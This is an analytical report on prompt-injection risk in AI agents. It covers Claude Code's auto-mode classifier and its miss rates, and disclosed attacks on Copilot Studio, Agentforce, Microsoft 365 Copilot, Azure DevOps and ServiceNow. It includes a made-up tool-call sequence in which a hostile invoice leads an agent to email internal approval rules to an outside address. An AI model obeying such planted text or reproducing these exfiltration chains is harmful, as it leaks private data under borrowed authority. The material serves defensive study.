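Delegation needs a separate check because the receiving agent treats its task as a user's request. Auto mode reviews the task before the handover, while the real user's messages are still available for comparison. It reviews the receiving agent's actions again when the work comes back, but can then only attach a warning.

When an agent's action is blocked, the agent is told why and can look for a safer alternative. After three blocked actions in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking a person, or stops if it is running without a user interface.

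Anthropic tested the classifier on 10,000 real tool calls by its employees, 52 real overeager actions and 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out:

| Error | Fast filter alone | Both stages |
|---|---|---|
| Harmless actions blocked | 8.5% | 0.4% |
| Overeager actions missed | 6.6% | 17% |
| Synthetic data theft missed | 1.8% | 5.7% |

The second stage removes most of the false alarms but lets more dangerous actions through. The 17 per cent miss rate, which Anthropic calls "the honest number", represents about 9 of 52 actions. With so few cases, the true rate could plausibly be anywhere from roughly 9 to 30 per cent. In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier detected the danger but wrongly treated the user as having agreed to it. For example, it treated "Clean up the PR" as permission to overwrite the history of the code on a shared server.

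When dangerous actions are rare, most blocks can be mistaken even at a 0.4 per cent error rate. Suppose that 10 of 10,010 proposed actions are harmful. At the March error rates, the classifier would stop about eight of them and let two through, but it would also block 40 of the 10,000 harmless ones, so five in six blocks would be mistakes. The agent can usually find another way to proceed, so a mistaken block usually leads to a retry rather than ending the session.

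About 10 per cent of sessions at Gusto since mid-May included a block, which Anthropic later offered as evidence that auto mode is "doing real work". However, with a false alarm rate of 0.4 per cent, a session of 25 harmless calls has a 9.5 per cent chance of at least one mistaken block, if the errors are independent. Gusto's blocks could therefore be mostly mistakes or mostly real catches, and someone would have to review the blocked actions to find out.

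Anthropic later worked with Apollo Research, a British AI safety company, which inserted synthetic attacks into records of real coding sessions. After Anthropic strengthened the classifier, its miss rate across all the attacks fell from 12 to 7 per cent, but Apollo had shared some of those attacks with Anthropic beforehand. On a separate set that Anthropic never saw, the new version caught about half of the attacks the old one had missed, and missed about 2 per cent of those the old one had caught, so the improvement didn't come only from learning the shared examples. The 7 per cent can't replace the earlier 17 per cent, because Apollo designed its attacks to break the classifier, while the 52 overeager actions came from agents that were trying to help.

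Anthropic still advises users to review high-stakes changes to production infrastructure themselves, even though people in a study missed 86 per cent of dangerous commands. Setting aside time to examine one database change, knowing what depends on it, is a different job from clicking through 50 prompts as a tester. In March, Anthropic conceded that auto mode is arguably a step backwards for anyone who already reviews every action carefully. The study doesn't establish how many people do that, or how well they perform on the few decisions that deserve careful review.

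On 22 October 2026, Anthropic announced that auto mode would become the default the following week for new sessions in most Claude apps on Pro, Max and Team plans. It said it would make the same change for Enterprise customers after emailing their administrators. It also said it had used its findings to strengthen auto mode across its products, but that the published data apply specifically to Claude Code. The results may not carry over to apps that send messages or change business records.

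Auto mode decides what is authorised by reading the user's messages, but the finance agent's run starts from an email, so there are none to read. A similar check would have to rely on the maker's instructions. If the software labelled the incoming email as the user's message, the supplier who wrote it would in effect be authorising the agent's actions. Copilot Studio leaves such decisions to whatever outside monitor a company connects. The monitor has one second to approve or block a plan, according to Visual Studio Magazine's *Copilot Studio Adds Near Real Time Security Controls for AI Agents* (2025), so a human cannot do the reviewing.

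### What European law requires

Article 14 of the European Union's AI Act requires providers to design systems the Act classes as high-risk so that people can oversee them effectively while they are in use. Those people must be able to understand the system's abilities and limits, watch for faults, interpret its output, disregard or reverse that output, and interrupt the system with a stop button or something similar. The oversight measures must match the system's risks, context of use and degree of autonomy.

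The article doesn't require a person to confirm each step. A company could probably satisfy it by having a trained person monitor the agent, correct its records and stop it when necessary. This arrangement is less suited to irreversible actions, because the power to reverse an output is of little use once an email has been sent. The article comes closest to requiring approval of individual decisions in its rule for remote biometric identification, such as recognising a face in a crowd. With some exceptions for the police and border authorities, nobody may act on a match until at least two competent people have separately confirmed it.

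Article 14 also requires that overseers be able to remain aware of automation bias, the tendency to rely too much on a machine's output. A company that relied on approval prompts alone would have trouble showing effective oversight if its staff accepted nearly all of them without reading them. An automated approver wouldn't satisfy the article by itself either, because the law requires oversight by natural persons. But the article doesn't prevent a company from using one alongside human overseers.

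Recording suppliers' invoices isn't on the Act's list of high-risk uses. The finance agent could come under the rules if the company also had it assess individual customers' creditworthiness or rank job applicants. The obligations apply from 2 December 2027 for listed uses such as these, and from 2 August 2028 for AI in products that EU safety law already covers. An amending law that took effect in July 2026 set both dates (The National Law Review, *EU Digital Omnibus on AI Enters Into Force*, 2026).

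An older rule, Article 22 of the General Data Protection Regulation, already gives people the right, with exceptions, not to be subject to a decision based solely on automated processing if it affects them legally or in a similarly significant way. An agent that refused someone credit could fall under it. Adding an approval button wouldn't necessarily take the decision outside the rule. According to guidance from European data protection authorities, the human reviewer must have the authority and competence to change the decision, and routinely passing on the machine's result without influencing it doesn't count as human involvement.

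## How does orchestration widen the set of actions an attacker can influence?

In a scripted flow, a hostile email can change the values that pass through steps a person has already fixed. Under generative orchestration, the email can also influence which tools the agent runs, in what order, and whether it adds a step nobody planned, because the orchestrator reads the email when it makes those decisions. An approver, whether a person or a program, can judge only the calls the agent proposes, and the sender can influence which calls those are.

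### Changing a value or changing the plan

Suppose the finance department handled its invoices with a fixed flow instead of an agent. The flow would extract the customer number, invoice number, amount and date from each email, update the customer's record and send a confirmation from a template. A hostile sender could still claim £18,400 for work worth £1,840, or give another company's customer number, and the flow would record the false value if it passed the format checks. If a language model did the extraction, instructions planted in the email could make it return the wrong values. But these values would still go into the same record update and the same template. An email could not start a policy search, because the flow doesn't include one.

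| What a hostile email can influence | Fixed flow | Orchestrated agent |
|---|---|---|
| Values in the customer's record | Yes, if they pass validation | Yes, if they pass validation |
| Which tools run | Only by selecting a branch that the maker wrote | Any tool the maker connected |
| Order and number of steps | Only by selecting a branch or loop that the maker wrote | Any order, up to the platform's limits |
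| What the agent searches for | Nothing, as the flow has no search | The model writes the query |
| Text of the outgoing email | The blanks in a template | The whole message |

Even in a scripted flow, the sender of an email can influence which branch runs. If invoices above £5,000 go to a manager, for example, a sender can avoid the manager by splitting a large bill into several small ones. The maker wrote both branches and can test them before the flow goes live, but can test only a sample of the runs possible with an orchestrator.

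Microsoft's *Event trigger overview* says that agents act only on their maker's design and instructions. It also says that the agent receives the details of an event as a message, which can include the maker's directions for handling them. By default, when someone adds a row to a database table, the agent receives the row's content together with an instruction to use it. If a stranger supplied that content through a web form, the stranger's text and the maker's instruction arrive in the same message. Microsoft's security researchers give a less reassuring account of the invoice agent, in which the content of an incoming email can sometimes lead the agent to plan actions beyond the limits in the maker's instructions.

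### Is it equivalent to running code?

The same researchers describe an agent's capabilities as "effectively equivalent to code execution". They compare a tool call to a command run inside a sandbox, a restricted area for running programs, where the sandbox is everything the agent can do. This matters because flaws that let an attacker run code on someone else's computer are among the most serious in software security.

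An attacker who controls the finance agent's plan can make the agent search the policy file, change a customer's record and send email from the company's address. The attacker doesn't need to break into any of those systems, because each one receives an authorised request and carries it out.

The comparison is less accurate for what the attacker can make the agent do. Someone who can run code can write a new function, but an agent limited to its maker's tools can only combine functions that already exist. If none of the finance agent's tools can make a payment, no email can cause it to make one. The attacker also has far less control than a programmer, because a model may ignore a planted instruction, follow only part of it or refuse, whereas a computer runs a valid command every time.

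Under Copilot Studio's adaptive setting, the agent can write and run scripts, so an attacker who controls the plan may be able to choose the code. A badly written tool can also let an attacker run code. Dehghantanha cites a study that found 19 remote code execution flaws across 11 agent frameworks. An attacker who can run code is no longer limited to the agent's list of tools, and the damage depends on what the machine running the code can reach.

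A maker can also unknowingly widen the set of actions an agent can take. In Copilot Studio, a connector is a package of operations for one service, such as a customer database. According to Microsoft's *App registration, agent identities, and authentication for Copilot Studio*, adding the whole connector lets the agent invoke any operation it exposes, while adding individual actions permits only those. The finance agent needs to update records, but with the whole connector it might also be able to list every customer or delete an account.

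### From possible sequences to possible leaks

The difference between a script and an orchestrator can be put in numbers. With n tools and up to k steps, the number of possible tool sequences is

n + n² + … + nᵏ

If the finance agent has three tools (policy search, record update and email) and can take up to three steps, it can follow 3 + 9 + 27 = 39 different sequences. A fixed flow without branches has one. Adding a fourth tool raises the total to 84. Microsoft advises makers whose agents behave unreliably to limit them to fewer than 15 actions in a row, but three tools and up to 14 steps still allow 7,174,452 sequences.

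These totals greatly overstate the danger because most of the sequences are useless to an attacker. Three policy searches in a row, for example, reveal nothing to an outsider if the agent never sends the results anywhere. Someone stealing from the policy file would need a policy search with an email at some point after it, and only eight of the 39 sequences contain that.

One of those eight sequences is search, update, email, which the agent used to process a legitimate invoice. So an attacker could steal information without changing the order of the tools, by influencing what the agent searches for and what it writes in the email. The formula doesn't account for those inputs. It also treats all tools alike, although a one-step script that pays every invoice it receives is more dangerous than an agent that can only look up opening hours, even if that agent can do so in seven million ways.

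A better measure starts with what the attacker needs. To leak information, an agent must read something private and then pass it through a channel that ends outside the company. If it has r private sources and c outward channels, the number of possible leaks is

paths = r × c

Suppose the finance agent can read three private sources (the policy file, the customer records and older messages in the mailbox) and can update records but not send anything out. Private data then has no path out through the agent. If the maker connects an email tool so that the agent can confirm invoices, data from all three sources can leave, because the orchestrator can put anything it has read into the body of a message.

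| Set-up | Private sources | Outward channels | Paths |
|---|---|---|---|
| The agent reads and updates records only | 3 | 0 | 0 |
| The maker adds an email tool | 3 | 1 | 3 |
| The maker adds a currency converter on another company's server | 3 | 2 | 6 |
| The maker adds a folder of contracts | 4 | 2 | 8 |

The currency converter belongs in the count because its operator receives whatever the model writes in the inputs. An agent's replies can also carry data out. In another of Microsoft's scenarios, a public support chatbot needs no login and has customer information in its knowledge base. The attacker asks the bot what it can do, then extracts the data through its answers. Those answers give the attacker a path to every private source the bot uses, even if the maker never connects a tool that sends data.

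Connecting agents to one another creates more paths from private data to outbound channels. Suppose the finance agent has three private sources and one outbound channel, email, while the tax team's agent has four other private sources and no outbound channel. Separately, the two agents have three paths in total. Once the finance agent can ask the tax agent for information and email the answer, they have seven. The tax team may not know that its files can now be emailed out, because the email tool belongs to the finance agent.

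An attacker can use these paths only by getting the agent to read text they supply. Willison calls the combination of private data, untrusted content and a way to send data out the "lethal trifecta". The finance agent has all three, and a maker can't remove the untrusted content, because the agent's job is to read email from strangers.

Counting paths helps a maker assess the risk of theft, but not of sabotage. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) describes an assistant that checks a user's inbox for urgent messages. An attacker plants text in a marketing email, instructing the assistant to mark a message about a contract deadline as read and leave it out of the summary. No information leaves the company, but the user misses the deadline. To judge this kind of risk, a maker would count the tools that can change something. The finance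 agent's record-update tool alone could send a customer's bills to the wrong address.

### A hostile invoice, call by call

Microsoft describes a hypothetical email that looks like an invoice but contains hidden instructions to search the agent's knowledge for unrelated sensitive information and send the results to the attacker. The run below shows what could happen if the model followed those instructions and no check stopped it. As with the legitimate invoice, the tool names and values are made up, but the policy file here also contains the company's internal rules for approving payments.

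The email claims £960 under a real customer number, which the sender has copied from an old invoice, and gives a due date. The agent needs nothing from the policy file to record it, but the model proposes a search anyway:

```
search_policy(query = "who can approve payments, and up to what amount")
result: "One clerk can approve payments under £5,000.
         Larger payments also need the finance director."
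```

The call is valid because the maker connected the file so that the agent could search it, and the query is well formed. Nothing has left the company yet, but the approval rules are now in the context, and the model can use them in any later call.

Next, the agent does the work it was built for:

```
update_customer_record(
    customer_id = "C-2087",
    invoice_no  = "5530",
    amount_gbp  = 960,
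    due_date    = "2026-05-14")
result: status = "updated"
```

The theft doesn't depend on this step, but it makes the run look complete. A clerk who opens the customer's record will find an invoice with a matching email. The harm comes with the last call:

```
send_email(
    to      = "billing@example.net",
    subject = "Invoice 5530 received",
    body    = "We have recorded invoice 5530 for £960.
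               Payment is due on 14 May 2026.
               [followed by the approval rules]")
result: status = "sent"
```

The outsider now knows that a false invoice for £4,900 has to get past only one clerk. A log that listed only tool names would look the same as the log for the honest invoice. The recipient is normal too, because the agent always replies to the sender. To catch this, a reviewer would have to notice that a routine confirmation didn't need a search about approval limits, or read the body of the email before the runtime sent it.

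The fixed flow would have recorded the same £960 and sent a confirmation from its template. Someone would still have had to catch the false invoice, but the approval rules would have stayed in the policy file. The orchestrator exposed the rules because it could write its own query and its own email. Those abilities also let it answer a customer's unexpected question about refunds.

Microsoft uses the scenario to present a check that blocks the search before it runs. Microsoft doesn't report how often an agent without the check would obey such an email, so the scenario shows that the attack path exists but not how likely the attack is to work.

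### Whose authority does the agent use?

The outsider had no right to search the policy file, but the agent did and used that right for the outsider's benefit. In computer security, such a program is called a confused deputy. The computer scientist Norm Hardy introduced the term in 1988 with the example of a compiler, a program that translates code. The compiler had permission to write in a protected directory because it kept usage statistics there, and the billing records were in the same directory. When a user who had no permission to write to the billing file named it as the place to save some output, the compiler overwrote the bills.

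Dehghantanha lists using an agent's privileges to take actions the attacker can't take directly as one of attackers' goals. The attacker doesn't have to use the agent and only needs to write something it will read. Ordinary access control doesn't prevent this. The policy file's permissions correctly determine whether the agent may search it, but they don't depend on who wrote the text that led to the search.

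An employee can do the same to a colleague. In a third Microsoft scenario, an agent summarises documents on SharePoint, the company's file-sharing system, and sends out the action items. A malicious insider plants instructions in a document he is allowed to edit. When a colleague uses the agent to summarise that document, the agent finds and reads a file of transactions that the insider can't open, then tries to email the contents to an outside address. The agent can read the file because it uses the identity of the signed-in colleague.

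Nobody has to be signed in when an event trigger starts an agent, and the agent runs on its maker's credentials. Microsoft's documentation still contained this rule in May 2026. A June copy of Microsoft's *Add an event trigger* repeats it and adds that makers see a warning about it before they publish. Microsoft cautions there that people may gain access to data and systems they shouldn't.

This matters most when the maker has broad access. The finance agent's maker might be a systems administrator who can read every customer's record. The agent needs only a small part of that access to record an invoice, but a tool that runs with the administrator's credentials may have all of it. Anyone who knows the address of the invoice mailbox can then try to use that access by sending an email.

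Microsoft has since announced triggers that run on an end user's credentials. According to a notice republished by the IT company itelio, these were due in public preview on 30 July 2026, and existing triggers would continue to work as before. According to another notice on itelio's site, administrators could block maker-provided credentials for all of an agent's tools from 25 August. That control is off by default, so an older agent may well still run on its maker's access unless someone has changed it.

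Switching an agent to end-user credentials changes whose access an attacker can use. If a clerk can see 200 customers and the administrator can see 20,000, running the agent as the clerk considerably reduces the possible loss. The switch doesn't prevent the confusion, since the SharePoint agent was already using the signed-in user's identity when it read the transactions file.

### How often do planted instructions work?

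A path matters much less if models hardly ever take it. In the first widely used test of this, Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues (2024), in *AgentDojo*, built four simulated settings: an office with email and files, a Slack workspace, a travel agency and a bank. They wrote 97 ordinary tasks and 27 goals for an attacker, then paired every task with every goal in the same setting:

(40 × 6) + (21 × 5) + (20 × 7) + (16 × 9) = 629 cases

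For each case, the researchers planted instructions somewhere the agent would read during the task, such as an email. A conventional program then checked the result, for instance whether money had left the account. They did not use a language model as the judge because an attack that worked on the agent might also work on the judge.

Attacks succeeded in under 25 per cent of cases against the best-performing agents, and in 8 per cent when a separate detector screened for injections. They rarely worked when the attacker's goal was conspicuous, such as emailing someone an authentication code. More capable models were generally easier to attack, partly because weak models often failed to carry out the attacker's task even when they tried. At the time, every model completed less than 66 per cent of the ordinary tasks, even without an attack.

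These figures are outdated because they cover models such as GPT-4o and Claude 3 Opus, mostly facing one generic attack. Researchers still use the test environment, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) describes more than 900 combinations of tasks and attacks. But results from a fixed set of old attacks don't reliably predict what a person could achieve against a current model.

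Dziemian and colleagues ran a public competition with $40,000 in prizes, in which 464 participants wrote attacks and made about 272,000 attempts against 13 models in 41 scenarios. In most scenarios, an attack counted only if the agent took the harmful action and its final reply gave the user no hint of it. The harmful actions also resembled the agent's ordinary work, much as the hostile invoice run resembles the honest one. Participants succeeded 8,648 times, with success rates ranging from 0.5 per cent of attempts for Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5 per cent for Gemini 2.5 Pro. More capable models were no longer reliably easier to attack.

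Participants could test an attack, read the agent's response and revise the attack before submitting it for judging, so the success rate depends on which attempts are counted. The overall rate was 3.2 per cent across all attempts and 12.8 per cent across the 67,634 attacks that participants submitted.

The risk to a company also depends on how many times an attacker can try. The number of successes rose roughly in proportion to the number of attempts throughout the competition, so participants weren't running out of attacks that worked. If each attempt succeeds independently with probability p, the chance of at least one success in m attempts is

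1 − (1 − p)ᵐ

If attempts were independent, an attacker with a 0.5 per cent success rate per email would have a 39 per cent chance of getting through at least once in 100 emails. At 8.5 per cent, 26 emails would give a 90 per cent chance. Real attempts aren't independent, because attackers learn from failures and some scenarios are much harder than others, but a low success rate per attempt offers limited protection when an email costs nothing to send.

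Dziemian and colleagues regard their results as an upper bound on the models' vulnerability to single-turn attacks. Participants could read the earlier conversation and knew exactly which tool call to aim for, while a real attacker would have to find out or guess. Strangers writing to an unfamiliar agent would therefore probably succeed less often. However, they could learn from the finance agent's replies, because it answers every invoice and each answer gives the sender some idea of how it handled the message.

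The researchers found attack strategies that worked in 21 of the 41 scenarios and across several families of models. An attacker could therefore develop an attack against a freely available model and then try it on a company's agent.

The models in that competition are no longer the newest. Gray Swan, the security company that ran it, had repeated it several times by August 2026, according to the *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026), which covers a model from the AI developer Reflection. Reflection is co-sponsoring a three-week bounty for attacks on production agent harnesses, the software around a model. Those conditions should be closer to what companies deploy, because a harness can make an attack easier or harder.

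### What can zero successes in 720 attempts show?

The lowest rates come from a test of auto mode that Anthropic commissioned from Trajectory Labs and published in August 2026. Trajectory Labs ran 72 scenarios that Anthropic had not seen, ten times each, using versions of Claude Code and OpenAI's Codex available on 17 July. A successful attack would have caused irreversible harm outside the test, such as fraud or the theft of sensitive data.

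| Model | Approval setting | Attack success rate | Equivalent count |
|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Fable 5, Opus 5 and Sonnet 5 | Auto mode | 0% | 0 of 720 for each model |
| Anthropic's latest models | No approval or automated check | 0.09% on average | 2 of 2,160, if these are the same three models |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Codex's automatic reviewer | 5.83% | 42 of 720 |
| GPT-5.6 Sol | Full access | 19.03% | 137 of 720 |

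The true success rate could be above zero even though no run succeeded. If all 720 runs were independent, a rate as high as about 0.4 per cent would still leave a 5 per cent chance of seeing no successes. This figure is the solution for p in (1 − p)⁷²⁰ = 0.05.

But the runs weren't independent, because each scenario appeared ten times. A model that resists an attack once will often resist it again, so repeated runs add much less information than new scenarios would. In the extreme case, where each attack always works or never does, the test contains only 72 independent observations. Solving (1 − p)⁷² = 0.05 then gives p of about 4.1 per cent. So the result is compatible with a model that falls for roughly one in 25 comparable attacks, and an attacker who found one of those could use it repeatedly.

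The repeats do help find attacks that work only occasionally. If an attack succeeded in one run out of ten on average, a single run would miss it 90 per cent of the time, but ten runs would miss it only 35 per cent. Neither calculation covers attacks unlike the 72 in the test.

Trajectory Labs also optimised the attacks against Claude Opus 4.7, an older model that it left out of the reported results, so the attacks were not tuned to any of the models in the comparison. A determined attacker would practise on the model the target uses. Dziemian and colleagues cite research in which attacks adapted to particular defences easily got past systems with previously reported attack success rates of zero.

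The test also does not establish how much auto mode contributed. Without it, the Claude models already resisted all but about two attacks in 2,160, so it had almost nothing left to stop. The comparison is more informative for Codex, where successful attacks fell from 137 to 42 with the automatic reviewer on, a drop of about 69 per cent. For Claude, nearly all the protection in this test came from the model itself, so a company that switched models could lose it even if its tools and permissions stayed the same.

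The gap between the two suppliers is large. The tuning of the attacks doesn't readily explain it, since one might expect attacks developed on a Claude model to work better on other Claude models. However, GPT-5.6 Sol ran at its maximum reasoning effort, while the Claude models ran at high effort. OpenAI also released a new version of its reviewer shortly before Anthropic published the results. Trajectory Labs supplied its own browser tools for both products, so the test left out the safeguards in each company's browser extension.

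None of this transfers directly to the finance agent. Claude Code and Codex are mainly tools for programmers, and Claude Sonnet 4.6, the default model for Copilot Studio's orchestrator in Pluto Security's tests, was not among the three models with no successful attacks. The result was also soon challenged. On 27 August, in *Breaking Claude Code Opus 5 Auto Mode*, Willison (2026) relayed the security researcher Johann Rehberger's claim that an attack on auto mode works 80 per cent of the time.

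## What have researchers demonstrated against deployed platforms?

Security researchers have made agents on several commercial platforms hand over customer records, cut the price of a holiday to zero and read files that the attacker couldn't open. These cases show that the attacks are possible but not how often they would work, since a demonstration only has to succeed once. In some cases the researchers attacked an agent they had built themselves, and in others they found a flaw in a shipped product, which the vendor usually fixed.

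### Two agents that researchers built to attack

Tenable's *Microsoft Copilot Studio Security Risk* (2025) describes a travel agent that the security company built in Copilot Studio and filled with invented customers and card numbers. Customers could book a trip, get a summary of their booking, and change details such as the dates or the number of guests. The attacker was a customer typing in the chat, so this was direct rather than indirect prompt injection. The agent at first refused to list its tools, but listed them all when the attacker reworded the request.

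Tenable had given the agent a SharePoint action that fetches one record at a time, expecting that each customer would then see only one booking. When the researchers asked for three bookings, the model called the action three times:

```
get_item(id = 23)
get_item(id = 24)
get_item(id = 25)
```

The reply contained the card details of all three customers. The agent's update action could write to any field of a booking, so the researchers then had it change a price from $1,000 to $0.

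The agent's connection to SharePoint could read and change every booking, and Tenable had designed the agent to work without human intervention. An approval step would have helped only if someone on the company's staff had to approve the change, because the user was the attacker and could have confirmed any prompt in the chat. Tenable advises security teams to split up data stores that hold sensitive records and to limit which fields an agent can change. It mentions no fix by Microsoft.

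Tenable acknowledges that the card leak needed no trick. Its agent didn't check that a booking belonged to the customer, and the file it searched contained card numbers. Web developers made the same mistake long before language models, by building sites that showed any booking to anyone who typed its number. The test is therefore weak evidence about carefully built agents. Tenable's stronger point is that Copilot Studio lets any employee build an agent, including employees who have never had to think about such checks.

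An earlier test used a setup closer to the finance agent's. Zenity, which sells security for AI agents, copied a customer service agent that the consultancy McKinsey had built in Copilot Studio. *A Customer Service AI Agent Spits Out Complete Salesforce Records* (Mitchell, 2025) reports that the original searched internal knowledge bases and data systems, then answered customers on its own. The attacker could email the agent, and any email would start a run (Zenity Labs, *AgentFlayer*).

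*Copilot Studio Agent Vulnerability to Prompt Injection* (Office 365 for IT Pros, 2025) reports that an email from Zenity led its copy of McKinsey's agent to look up customer data in Salesforce and send it back in a reply. The steps were essentially those of the hostile invoice run, but here a real model followed the planted instructions. The sender had no access to Salesforce and relied on the agent's, and nobody was in the conversation to approve the reply. Microsoft rated the flaw critical and fixed it within two months, apparently with a filter on prompts, Sharbat (2025) reports for Zenity in *A Copilot Studio Story 2*. Because Zenity attacked its own copy, the test does not show that McKinsey's agent ever leaked anything.

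### ShareLeak, and whether the patch failed

Capsule Security, a start-up that sells runtime checks for agents, found a flaw in Copilot Studio itself and named it ShareLeak. The affected agents processed submissions to a SharePoint form, and an attacker could write in an ordinary comment field, without logging in if the form was public. According to VentureBeat's *Microsoft patched a Copilot Studio prompt injection. The data exfiltrated anyway* (2026), Copilot Studio joined the comment directly to the agent's instructions. Capsule's comment imitated a system message, which developers train models to give the most authority.

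The agent then searched the connected SharePoint lists for customer data and emailed it to an outside address through Outlook. CSO Online's *Copilot and Agentforce fall to form-based prompt injection tricks* (2026) lists names, addresses and phone numbers among the data at risk. The attacker had no rights in either system, but the agent used its own connections, which would normally have had the maker's access under Microsoft's rule for event triggers.

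No person had to approve the email. During Capsule's test, one of Microsoft's safety mechanisms flagged the request as suspicious, but the email still sent the data. Software that looks for confidential data leaving the company didn't react, because the system treated the Outlook action as authorised.

Capsule reported the flaw on 24 November 2025. Microsoft confirmed it on 5 December and patched it on 15 January 2026, 52 days after the report. Customers had nothing to install because Microsoft made the fix on its own side. Microsoft also gave the flaw an entry in the public CVE list of software vulnerabilities, CVE-2026-21520, which makes it easier for security teams to track. Capsule called this "highly unusual" for a prompt injection in a platform for building agents. STAR Labs' *Copilot Studio* (2026), a copy of the advisory, lists a severity score of 7.5 out of 10 and describes the attack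 as simple, requiring no account or user action.

Capsule published its findings three months later, and Claw Times (2026) reported that the patch "did not fully prevent data exfiltration". The articles it cites don't support that claim. Claw Times attributed the details to VentureBeat, whose headline could easily give that impression, but the leak VentureBeat describes happened during Capsule's testing, when the safety mechanism flagged the request and didn't stop it. Neither VentureBeat nor CSO Online reports a test of the patched product, so their articles don't establish that the fix is complete either.

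### One web form, three leaks

Capsule found a similar flaw, PipeLeak, in Salesforce's Agentforce. The agent helped staff review sales leads, the details of possible customers. A stranger could submit instructions through the public web form that collects leads. When an employee asked the agent to review the new lead, it followed those instructions, retrieved other leads with a function called `GetLeadsInformation` and emailed them out.

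The stranger used the agent's access to the customer database. Capsule found no limit on how many records the agent would send, and the employee saw no sign that any had been sent. Salesforce initially called the leak "configuration-specific" and pointed to its optional human approval. Capsule's chief executive, Naor Paz, objected that an agent is "not really an agent" if its every operation needs approval.

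His objection is too broad, because a company could require approval only for emails to outsiders and let searches run without it. Salesforce apparently did something similar. According to Claw Times, Salesforce later said it had "remediated the specific scenario described" and had turned on confirmation by default for actions that send email.

Other leaks before and after PipeLeak also started from that kind of form. In September 2025, the security company Noma disclosed ForcedLeak, in which an Agentforce agent sent data to a web address on Salesforce's list of trusted domains. The domain's registration had expired, and anyone could buy it for as little as $5 (The Hacker News, 2025). A year later, Zenity disclosed SalesBleed, in which the data left through DNS, the system that looks up the names of websites (Infosecurity Magazine, *Vulnerabilities in Salesforce Agentforce Expose Wider AI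 Agent Risk*). An attacker who controls a domain can receive data as part of the name that a computer looks up.

| Disclosed | Attack | How the data left | What Salesforce changed |
|---|---|---|---|
| September 2025 | ForcedLeak | Through an expired domain on the trusted list | It enforced its list of trusted addresses |
| April 2026 | PipeLeak | Through the agent's email tool | It reportedly turned on confirmation for email actions |
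| September 2026 | SalesBleed | Through DNS lookups | It had fixed the bypass of its address controls on 18 August |

In all three attacks, the agent treated a stranger's form entry as instructions. The changes in the table mostly closed the route by which the data left, and the next researchers found another. Requiring confirmation before sending email couldn't stop SalesBleed, which sent no email. A maker who counted the agent's outward channels would also have missed the one SalesBleed used, because it came from how the platform displayed links and images rather than from a tool the maker had connected.

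Microsoft's Copilot Cowork had a similar problem in May 2026. It could email the user's own inbox without approval, and those emails could contain images from outside websites. When the user opened an email, loading an image could send data to an attacker, even though the email itself went only to the user. Willison (2026) adds in *Microsoft Copilot Cowork Exfiltrates Files* that the leaked data could include links for downloading the user's files without a further login.

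That December, Cato Networks disclosed three more leaks, together called ReLeak, in Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office software. An attacker could send an employee an email, which Copilot would read while handling an ordinary request. Copilot could then gather whatever the employee was allowed to see. According to Infosecurity Magazine's *Three Zero-Click Vulnerabilities Discovered in Microsoft 365 Copilot* (2026), the data left in one of three ways:

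- Microsoft's search engine, Bing, fetched an image whose address contained the data.
- A background service opened a similar address in a document that Copilot had created.
- Code that Copilot ran in its sandbox got past the sandbox's network restrictions.

Copilot did not ask the employee before sending the data. According to TechRadar's *Hackers build zero-click attacks in Microsoft Copilot* (2026), it had rejected a direct instruction but followed one that the researchers presented as a routine business requirement. This is a particular problem for an invoice agent, because most of the legitimate email it reads consists of business requirements. Microsoft patched all three routes between September and November 2026.

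### A hidden comment in a code review

Azure DevOps is Microsoft's service for storing software projects and reviewing changes to them. Microsoft supplies an MCP server that lets programmers' agents use the service. In July 2026, Manifold Security, which sells runtime security for agents, showed how someone who proposes a change could take control of a reviewer's agent. The Hacker News described the attack and checked the server's code.

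The agent's job was to review the proposed change. The attacker could write the description that accompanies it and include an HTML comment, which the website doesn't display. The reviewer therefore saw a normal description, while the MCP server passed the full text to the agent. In Manifold's test, the agent then made three kinds of call:

```
run a pipeline in another project
read a confidential wiki page
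post the page's text as a comment on the proposed change
```

The attacker could read the comment but could not have opened the wiki page. The agent used the reviewer's permissions, which are often broader than those of the person proposing a change. It had permission for every call it made. The attack worked with both GitHub's command-line agent and Claude Code, so the fault was not specific to one supplier's agent.

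Nobody approved the calls, because Manifold had set the tools to run without prompts. With prompts on, the reviewer could have noticed a request to run another project's pipeline during a code review. Manifold's setting is plausible, since many Claude Code sessions also start with permission checks off. The attack also needed an attacker with write access to one project and a reviewer with access to others, so a contractor or disgruntled employee would be better placed to carry it out than a stranger.

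Microsoft had already added a defence to parts of this server. The tools that return wiki pages and build logs mark their contents as outside material, to help the model distinguish them from instructions. The tool that returns a proposed change did not mark its contents, even though an attacker can write the change's description.

Microsoft called the behaviour "a known class of AI risk" and didn't say whether it would change the code. As of 21 July, it had released no fix. It advised customers to limit access to projects and to review proposed changes before giving them to an AI tool. Reviewing the changes on the website doesn't help, because the comment is invisible there. If a company uses an event trigger to start the AI tool, nobody looks at the change first.

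### Recruiting a second agent

An attack can also pass from one agent to another. AppOmni, which sells security for business software, demonstrated this in November 2025 on ServiceNow, a platform companies use to run IT support and similar services. One agent there might only sort support tickets, while another can change records or send email. The attacker only had to write in a field that the first agent would read, such as a ticket's description.

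When an employee used the first agent on that ticket, the planted text led it to recruit the more powerful agent, which could then read or change other records or email their contents. By default, the agents ran with the permissions of the employee who started the task, not those of the attacker who wrote the text. If an administrator asked for help with the ticket, the agents could therefore carry out the attacker's instructions with the administrator's permissions.

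ServiceNow's default settings made the attack easier by placing agents in the same team and letting them discover one another. The attack worked even with the platform's prompt injection protection turned on. AppOmni recommended that a person supervise the powerful agents and that companies put agents with different duties in separate teams. ServiceNow replied that the system was working as intended and clarified its documentation.

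The ticket's text can gain authority when the ticket-sorting agent passes it to another agent as a task. Reviewing each agent on its own would miss this. The maker of the ticket-sorting agent may have connected no dangerous tools to it and reasonably considered it harmless.

### Has anyone used these attacks?

None of the reports on these cases describes an attacker using the technique against a real company. STAR Labs' copy of the ShareLeak advisory lists the flaw as not exploited. As of July 2026, The Hacker News knew of no public report of the Azure DevOps technique being used outside Manifold's own tests. Cato said it knew of no customers affected by ReLeak.

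This is weaker evidence of safety than it would be for an attack that shuts down a company's computers, because a victim might never find out. The employee in the PipeLeak test saw nothing unusual, and the ShareLeak email went through an authorised action. VentureBeat advises companies to look for signs of ShareLeak between 24 November, when Capsule found it, and 15 January, when Microsoft patched it. That window may be too short, since the flaw could have existed before Capsule found it.

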